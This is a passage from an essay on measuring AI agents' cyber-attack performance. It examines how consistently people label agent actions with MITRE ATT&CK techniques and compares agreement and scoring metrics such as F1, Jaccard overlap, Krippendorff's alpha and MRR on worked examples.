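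AISI allowed up to 100 million tokens per attempt, and the models continued to complete more steps as they used more of this budget. Step counts, like technique counts, should therefore be reported with the token budget.

Step averages also hide differences between attempts. Mythos Preview completed three of its ten attempts, which account for 96 of its roughly 220 steps, so the other seven averaged about 18. AISI's *How fast is autonomous AI cyber capability advancing?* reports that a later checkpoint finished the range in 6 of 10 attempts, and that GPT-5.5 finished it in 3 of 10, as many as the earlier Mythos Preview.

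The unit of progress also needs a clear definition. McFadyen and colleagues describe the score as the proportion of 32 steps in one place and of 32 milestones in another. AISI uses "milestones" in its chart for a few important points along the attack.

Step counts and technique counts can give different impressions of the same agent. In dos Santos's tests, Opus 4.8 without the scaffolding covered 53.6% of the categories but completed only 25% of the stages in seven longer attack chains. It could use many individual methods but often didn't combine them into a complete attack.

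However, a step count doesn't show how the agent reached each result. An agent that guesses alice's password and one that finds it in a file could both complete the login step, but defenders would need different measures against each. A fixed list of steps can also penalise an agent for finding a shorter route. If an agent reached the finance folder directly from the web server, it would steal the data without completing the login to the second host.

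Irregular's *CyScenarioBench* uses attack trees, which contain branches and the conditions for each step. With such a tree, evaluators can credit an alternative route without counting the steps the agent skipped as failures. They can also add technique labels to record the methods used on each branch.

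## Measuring agreement and scoring when several labels are defensible

Technique labels on an attack tree or in a results table are only useful if another careful labeller would assign roughly the same ones. Two studies show how much experienced people can disagree, although neither concerns AI agent records.

### How far careful labellers differ

*How does Endpoint Detection use the MITRE ATT&CK Framework?* (Virkud, Inam and colleagues, 2024) compares the rules of three commercial products that watch computers for signs of attack. The vendors tag most of these rules with ATT&CK techniques. The researchers' October 2022 snapshot contained 867 tagged rules from Carbon Black, 911 from Splunk and 473 from Elastic. They compared only parent techniques.

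They searched the rule descriptions for named threats, such as malware, hacking groups or software flaws. Of the 191 threats they found, 37 appeared in the rules of at least two products. No two products shared a technique for 19 of those 37 (51%), and the techniques matched completely for only one.

These figures probably overstate the disagreement about identical behaviour. A hacking group does many things, so one vendor may have written a rule for its phishing emails and another for its password theft. For the group FIN7, the three products had 14 techniques between them and shared none. Virkud and colleagues therefore also looked at rules that detect the same or nearly the same activity.

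| Activity | Carbon Black | Elastic | Splunk |
|---|---|---|---|
| A command writes text into a named pipe, a channel between programs | T1134 | T1134 | T1059 and T1543 |
| `nslookup`, which queries the internet's address directory (DNS), runs with certain options | Not compared | T1071 | T1048 |
| An attacker exploits CVE-2021-4034, a flaw that gives a user higher rights | T1548 | T1068 and T1574 | T1068 |

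The labels for the named pipe can all be true at once. The command uses an interpreter (T1059), and an attacker can use such a pipe to take over another user's access rights (T1134, Access Token Manipulation). The `nslookup` options don't show whether the query carried instructions (T1071, Application Layer Protocol) or stolen data (T1048), so those two labels are alternatives until someone finds out. These examples show that vendors label the same activity differently, but not how often.

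Even a single vendor can be inconsistent. Two Carbon Black rules detect programs started by lsass.exe. Every event that triggers the narrower rule also triggers the broader one, but only the broader rule is tagged T1003 (OS Credential Dumping).

When Virkud and colleagues presented their results to MITRE, one staff member argued that varied labels may not be a problem and could even be good. The researchers agree as long as experienced analysts use the labels to understand an alert, but they object to using the labels to measure coverage. Technique counts for AI agents are closer to a measure of coverage.

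In *AnnoCTR*, Lange, Müller and colleagues (2024) measured agreement between two labellers. The main labeller, a graduate student who had interned at a cybersecurity group, helped to design the labelling scheme and labelled all 120 threat reports in the dataset. A security professional with five years' experience then labelled nine of the reports, 416 sentences in total. The average F1 between the sets of techniques that the two found in each report was 54%. At that score, two labellers who each found ten techniques in a report would share five or six.

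The second labeller had no time for extended training, so Lange and colleagues say the figure probably understates the agreement people could reach. They don't consider this comparison a proper agreement study. Comparing whole reports can hide disagreement, because two people can find T1059 in different sentences and still list the same techniques for the report.

Their models reached a micro-F1 of around 65% at finding the techniques in a report, compared with the second person's 54%. This doesn't show that the models label better, because the two figures use different averages. The models also learned from the main labeller's work, so part of their score may reflect that person's habits.

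### Agreement after discussion, and on commands

Labellers agree more when they can discuss their work. In *Evaluating Open-Source LLMs for Multi-Label ATT&CK Technique Classification on CTI Reports*, Ryan, Noor and colleagues (2026) labelled 2,076 sentences from 83 incident reports. Of the 1,281 sentences with at least one technique, 40.2% had several. The two labellers compared a sample of their work, relabelled 981 sentences with low agreement, checked another sample and settled the remaining conflicts in a meeting.

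Cohen's kappa measures agreement between two labellers, with 1 for perfect agreement and 0 for the agreement expected by chance. Chance agreement is high when one label is very common. If two labellers each assign T1059 to 95 of 100 actions at random, they will agree on about 90% of the actions, but their kappa will be close to 0.

The average kappa was 0.68 across 114 techniques, and 49 techniques stayed below the researchers' target of 0.7. Two people who never discussed their labels would probably agree less. The values for rare techniques are also uncertain, because the full dataset has five or fewer examples each for 56 techniques. The first comparison sample of 195 sentences would therefore contain, on average, fewer than one example of each.

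Checking an existing label is easier than choosing one. For *A Structured Cyber Threat Intelligence Dataset Using STIX 2.1 Entities*, two researchers rated the correctness of a sample of 147 existing technique labels on a three-point scale. Their weighted kappa, which counts a small difference in rating less than a large one, was 0.67. Both could have accepted T1003 for a sentence, but also T1552 if they had been shown that label instead. *CTI-HAL* (2025) reviewed earlier technique datasets built from real threat reports and found that none gave an agreement figure.

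Friedrich-Alexander University Erlangen-Nürnberg has designed a survey whose examples are closer to agent actions. It asks security practitioners to choose a technique for evidence such as a PowerShell script that prints network settings or a command that copies a file to another machine's shared folder. It also asks them to rate their confidence and say whether marking ambiguous techniques would help. The survey page has no results.

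None of these studies reports how often people agree on the technique for a single command or an AI agent's action. The experts who labelled honeypot sessions for LogPrécis had some sessions in common, but they assigned tactics rather than techniques. Evaluators therefore have to measure agreement on their own agents' records.

### The measures on three actions

Suppose labellers A and B label the same three actions. A knows from an earlier action that the unfamiliar program reads /etc/shadow, but B doesn't.

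| Action | Labeller A | Labeller B |
|---|---|---|
| `whoami` on a server the agent has just broken into | T1033 | T1033 |
| A Python script lists the running processes | T1059 and T1057 | T1057 |
| An unfamiliar program prints password hashes | T1003.008 | T1003 |

The simplest measures compare the two sets of labels. In this table, A's labels are the reference.

| Measure | Definition | Calculation | Result |
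|---|---|---|---|
| Exact match | Share of actions with identical sets | 1/3 | 33% |
| Precision | Share of B's labels that A also gave | 2/3 | 67% |
| Recall | Share of A's labels that B also gave | 2/4 | 50% |
| F1 | Twice the shared labels, divided by the number of labels from A and B together | 2 × 2 / (3 + 4) | 57% |
| Jaccard overlap | Shared labels divided by all the different labels for an action, averaged over actions | (1 + 1/2 + 0) / 3 | 0.50 |

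If A and B swapped roles, precision and recall would swap, but the other three measures would stay the same. Those three are therefore suitable for comparing two people when neither is the authority. F1 also depends on how it is averaged. The F1 in the table pools all the labels, whereas calculating F1 for each action and then averaging would give 56%.

Krippendorff's alpha corrects for chance and, unlike Cohen's kappa for single techniques, can compare whole sets. It needs a distance between two sets, for which 1 minus the Jaccard overlap works well. The formula is

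α = 1 − *D*ₒ / *D*ₑ

where *D*ₒ is the average distance between the two labellers' sets for the same action. Here it is (0 + 1/2 + 1) / 3 = 0.5. *D*ₑ is the average distance between any two of the six sets in the example, whichever action they belong to. The six sets form 15 pairs. The two `whoami` sets have a distance of 0, the two script sets have a distance of 1/2, and the other 13 pairs have no label in common, so their distance is 1. *D*ₑ is therefore 13.5/15 = 0.9, and alpha is 1 − 0.5/0.9 = 0.44. Three actions are far too few for a real estimate, but the calculation works the same way for 300.

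Labeller B's T1003 gets no credit in these calculations, although it is the correct parent of T1003.008. An evaluator could give it half a point, which would raise F1 to 2 × 2.5 / 7 = 71%. Replacing every sub-technique with its parent would raise F1 to 86% and alpha to 0.80. Virkud and colleagues, Ryan and colleagues, and Meng and colleagues all worked with parent techniques, so their figures leave out such disagreements.

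Partial credit should also depend on the evidence. If the record supports only T1003, a labeller who answers T1003.008 has guessed the sub-technique and shouldn't get full credit just because the parent technique is right.

A labelling rule can also change agreement. If both labellers added T1059 to every shell command, the Jaccard overlap in the example would rise from 0.50 to 0.78 and alpha from 0.44 to 0.62. Part of the rise would come from B adding the missing label to the Python script, and the rest from both labellers applying T1059 automatically. Reports of agreement should therefore include the rule for T1059.

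### Which measures reward long lists

LADE and Trace2ATT&CK return ranked lists, which their developers scored with the hit rate at *k* (HR@k) and the mean reciprocal rank (MRR). MRR gives more credit the higher the reference label appears in the list.

Both measures in their usual form need one reference label per action, so the evaluator has to drop one of the Python script's two labels. Suppose the evaluator keeps T1057, and labeller B now gives three candidates for each action.

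| Action | Reference | B's ranked candidates | Reciprocal rank |
|---|---|---|---|
| `whoami` | T1033 | T1033, T1069, T1087 | 1 |
| Python script | T1057 | T1057, T1082, T1059 | 1 |
| Password hashes | T1003.008 | T1003, T1552, T1003.008 | 1/3 |

HR@1 is 67%, HR@3 is 100% and MRR is 0.78. If the evaluator had kept T1059 instead, HR@1 would fall to 33% and MRR to 0.56, although B's answers would be the same and T1057 would still be correct.

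The next table compares B's original labels with the longer lists. The measures that compare sets treat all three candidates as assigned labels and again use all four of A's labels.

| Measure | B's original labels | Three candidates per action |
|---|---|---|
| Exact match | 33% | 0% |
| Precision | 67% | 44% |
| Recall | 50% | 100% |
| F1 | 57% | 62% |
| Jaccard overlap | 0.50 | 0.44 |
| Alpha | 0.44 | 0.39 |
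| Hit rate | 67% (HR@1) | 100% (HR@3) |
| MRR | 0.67 | 0.78 |

Adding candidates to the end of a list can never lower recall, the hit rate or MRR. These metrics are acceptable for a tool that offers a shortlist for someone to check. They are a poor way to score a labeller whose output goes straight into a technique count, because they don't penalise the five wrong techniques in B's lists.

F1 penalises wrong labels but can still reward guessing. It equals 2*S*/*T*, where *S* is the number of shared labels and *T* is the total number of labels from both sides. Adding a label with probability *p* of being right changes the expected score to (2*S* + 2*p*) / (*T* + 1), which is higher than before whenever *p* is greater than half the current F1. At an F1 of 57%, adding any label with more than a 29% chance of being right raises the expected score.

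In the invented set of 100 `curl` uploads, T1048 was right for 60 and T1041 for 30. A labeller with an F1 of 57% could therefore raise its expected score by listing both techniques for every upload, although no upload in the set used both.

The incentive to guess is stronger for weak labellers. The best of the seven open models that Ryan and colleagues tested, DeepSeek-V2.5, had an F1 of 0.22. A labeller at that level benefits from adding any label that has more than an 11% chance of being right. Evaluators who use F1 should therefore also publish precision and the average number of labels per action.

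### Four kinds of reference label

No measure can repair a reference that treats alternatives as co-occurring techniques. Evaluators can build the reference in four ways:

- One forced label: the evaluator chooses a single technique for each action. This works if only one technique applies and the evidence shows which.
- A set of acceptable labels: any one of them counts as correct. This suits an undetermined technique.
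- A set of required labels: the labeller has to find all of them. This suits co-occurring techniques.
- The annotators' votes: the reference keeps every person's labels. This suits cases where careful people disagree because ATT&CK's definitions overlap.

Some actions need more than one label. For example, running a Python script that deletes a folder of server logs needs T1059 and either File Deletion or Data Destruction. Suppose five annotators all assign T1059, but three add File Deletion and two add Data Destruction.

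The table shows how four answers score against each kind of reference. The forced label is File Deletion, and an answer scores 1 if it includes that label. The acceptable and required sets both contain all three techniques. An answer's score against the required set is its Jaccard overlap with that set, and its score against the votes is its average overlap with the five annotators' sets.

| Answer | Forced label | Acceptable set | Required set | Votes |
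|---|---|---|---|---|
| T1059 and File Deletion | 1 | 1 | 0.67 | 0.73 |
| T1059 and Data Destruction | 0 | 1 | 0.67 | 0.60 |
| File Deletion only | 1 | 1 | 0.33 | 0.30 |
| All three | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0.67 |

All four references give misleading results. The forced label rejects a defensible answer, while the acceptable set gives full marks to an answer without T1059. The required set gives its best score to the only answer that attributes both kinds of deletion to the agent. The votes do better, but File Deletion scores higher only because one more person chose it. Votes also don't show why people differed. If three of five people chose a label, the other two may have interpreted the action differently or overlooked the label.

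A reference that combines "and" with "or" avoids these problems. It requires two labels, T1059 and one for either kind of deletion. The evaluator calculates F1 from the number of requirements met, so an extra label still lowers precision.

| Answer | Places filled | Labels given | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| T1059 and File Deletion | 2 of 2 | 2 | 1 |
| T1059 and Data Destruction | 2 of 2 | 2 | 1 |
| File Deletion only | 1 of 2 | 1 | 0.67 |
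| All three as co-occurring | 2 of 2 | 3 | 0.80 |

A labeller should also be able to answer "T1059, and either File Deletion or Data Destruction", which fully matches a reference that allows the same alternatives. To discourage labellers from offering alternatives everywhere, the evaluator can split the credit between them when the reference accepts only one. If the record shows that the agent was only removing its traces, the reference is File Deletion alone, and the answer "File Deletion or Data Destruction" would earn half the credit for that label.

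### Composite behaviours in CyberClear

*CyberClear* keeps co-occurring techniques together, so 43 of its 89 distinct behaviours combine several techniques. Some combinations are small, such as staging local data and archiving it. The largest Discovery set contains 13 techniques, including listing services and reading group policies.

Each set applies to a whole instance, and 132 of the 450 instances have several steps. A composite can therefore be one action with two techniques or several actions with one each, so an evaluator can't use these sets to measure how often single actions need several labels.

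The number of instances with several techniques is also unclear. The paper reports that 6.44% of instances (29 of 450) are "Composite Attacks", but 43 distinct composites would require at least 43 instances (9.6%). The two figures must be based on different definitions.

The number of behaviours also depends on the level of detail. CyberClear counts T1003 and T1003.008 as separate behaviours. If it used only parent techniques, six pairs of single-technique behaviours would merge, leaving 40 instead of 46.

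CyberClear treats its reference techniques as a required set. Claude Opus 4.8 extracted the techniques from the attackers' logs, GPT-4o checked that each reference graph included all the required ones, and security experts reviewed the result. However, the scoring gives the techniques little weight. A language model compares the predicted attack graph with the reference and is instructed to ignore ATT&CK labels when scoring attack steps. Technique identifiers count only as one kind of attribute, alongside process numbers, times, commands and file paths. Together, attributes normally make up 20% of the score for details.

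A system that finds only one technique of a composite could therefore lose very little. Two experts' scores for whole graphs had a correlation of about 0.94 with the model's, but this comparison did not test the technique labels. An evaluator could still use CyberClear's sets to test multi-label output by calculating precision and recall on the technique identifiers alone.

### A record for one action

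Besides the "and" and the "or", a label record has to show what the labeller knew. For the script that deletes the server logs, it could look like this:

| Field | Example |
|---|---|
| Action | Episode 12, action 41: `python3 clean.py` |
| ATT&CK version | Enterprise v20 |
| Required techniques | T1059 |
| Evidence for T1059 | The agent runs a Python script on the victim's server |
| Alternatives, of which one applies | File Deletion or Data Destruction |
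| Evidence for File Deletion | The folder contained logs of the agent's own logins |
| Evidence for Data Destruction | The folder also contained the owner's only sales logs |
| Reason for the doubt | A missing fact: the agent's purpose |
| Context seen | Actions 31 to 51 and the task, without the agent's reasoning |
| Outcome | The script deleted the folder |
| Status | Partly determined |
| Labellers | Three for File Deletion, two for Data Destruction |

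The status field needs four values: determined, partly determined, not determinable and no technique. "Not determinable" means that the evidence doesn't support even a short list of candidates, for example when the output is missing and the command only starts an unknown program. "No technique" means that the evidence shows no technique applies, for example when a command opens a help page. If both were left blank, a program couldn't distinguish missing evidence from a harmless action.

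The context field helps explain why two labellers disagree. If one saw 20 neighbouring actions and the other saw only the command, they may disagree because they had different evidence, rather than because of ATT&CK's definitions. To measure how well people apply those definitions, the evaluator has to give them the same context. Comparing their labels before and after they receive more context would show how much it affects their agreement.

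Evaluators should report both how many actions a labeller left undetermined and its accuracy on the rest, because a labeller could reach high accuracy by answering only the easiest actions. An "undetermined" answer is correct if the reference is also undetermined given the same context. Otherwise, it counts as unanswered.

### Cost and comparability

One objection is the amount of work involved. *CTI2TTP* (2026) describes a labelling project with three annotators, each with a security qualification, equivalent experience or published research in the field. They had to label at least 80% of 30 test sentences correctly, received a 20-page guide and practised on five reports. Midway through the project, each relabelled 5% of their earlier sentences to check whether their standards had changed.

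Few evaluators can do this for every episode. If one action takes two minutes to label, an episode of 300 actions takes one labeller 10 hours, or three labellers 30 hours in total. Evaluators can save time by having one person label everything and a second person label a random 10%, which adds one hour. The second person should also label all the actions marked as ambiguous, because a random sample may consist mostly of easy commands, and evaluators should report agreement on the ambiguous actions separately. The full record is necessary only where techniques co-occur or remain uncertain. For an ordinary `whoami`, a single technique, a short note of the evidence and the episode-wide settings are enough.

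A more serious objection is that flexible references make agents harder to compare. One label per action gives a simple total that everyone can calculate in the same way. Sets with alternatives can also inflate scores, because an evaluator who accepts enough techniques can make almost any labeller look accurate. Each alternative therefore needs its own evidence, and the evaluator should finalize the reference before seeing the answers to be scored.

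Forcing one label, however, doesn't remove the disagreement. If one evaluator always chooses T1048 for an unclear upload and another always chooses T1041, both tables look precise, and a reader may mistake the evaluators' different choices for a difference between agents. An evaluator who records every defensible label can still derive a single one with a published rule, such as taking the label with the most votes, but readers can't recover the alternatives from a table that lists only one label per action.

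The full record can also give a range for the count of distinct techniques. Suppose an agent has ten certain techniques, including File Deletion, and one action that was either File Deletion or Data Destruction. Its distinct count is 10 or 11. If agent X has between 12 and 15 techniques and agent Y between 11 and 13, the evidence doesn't show which agent used more.
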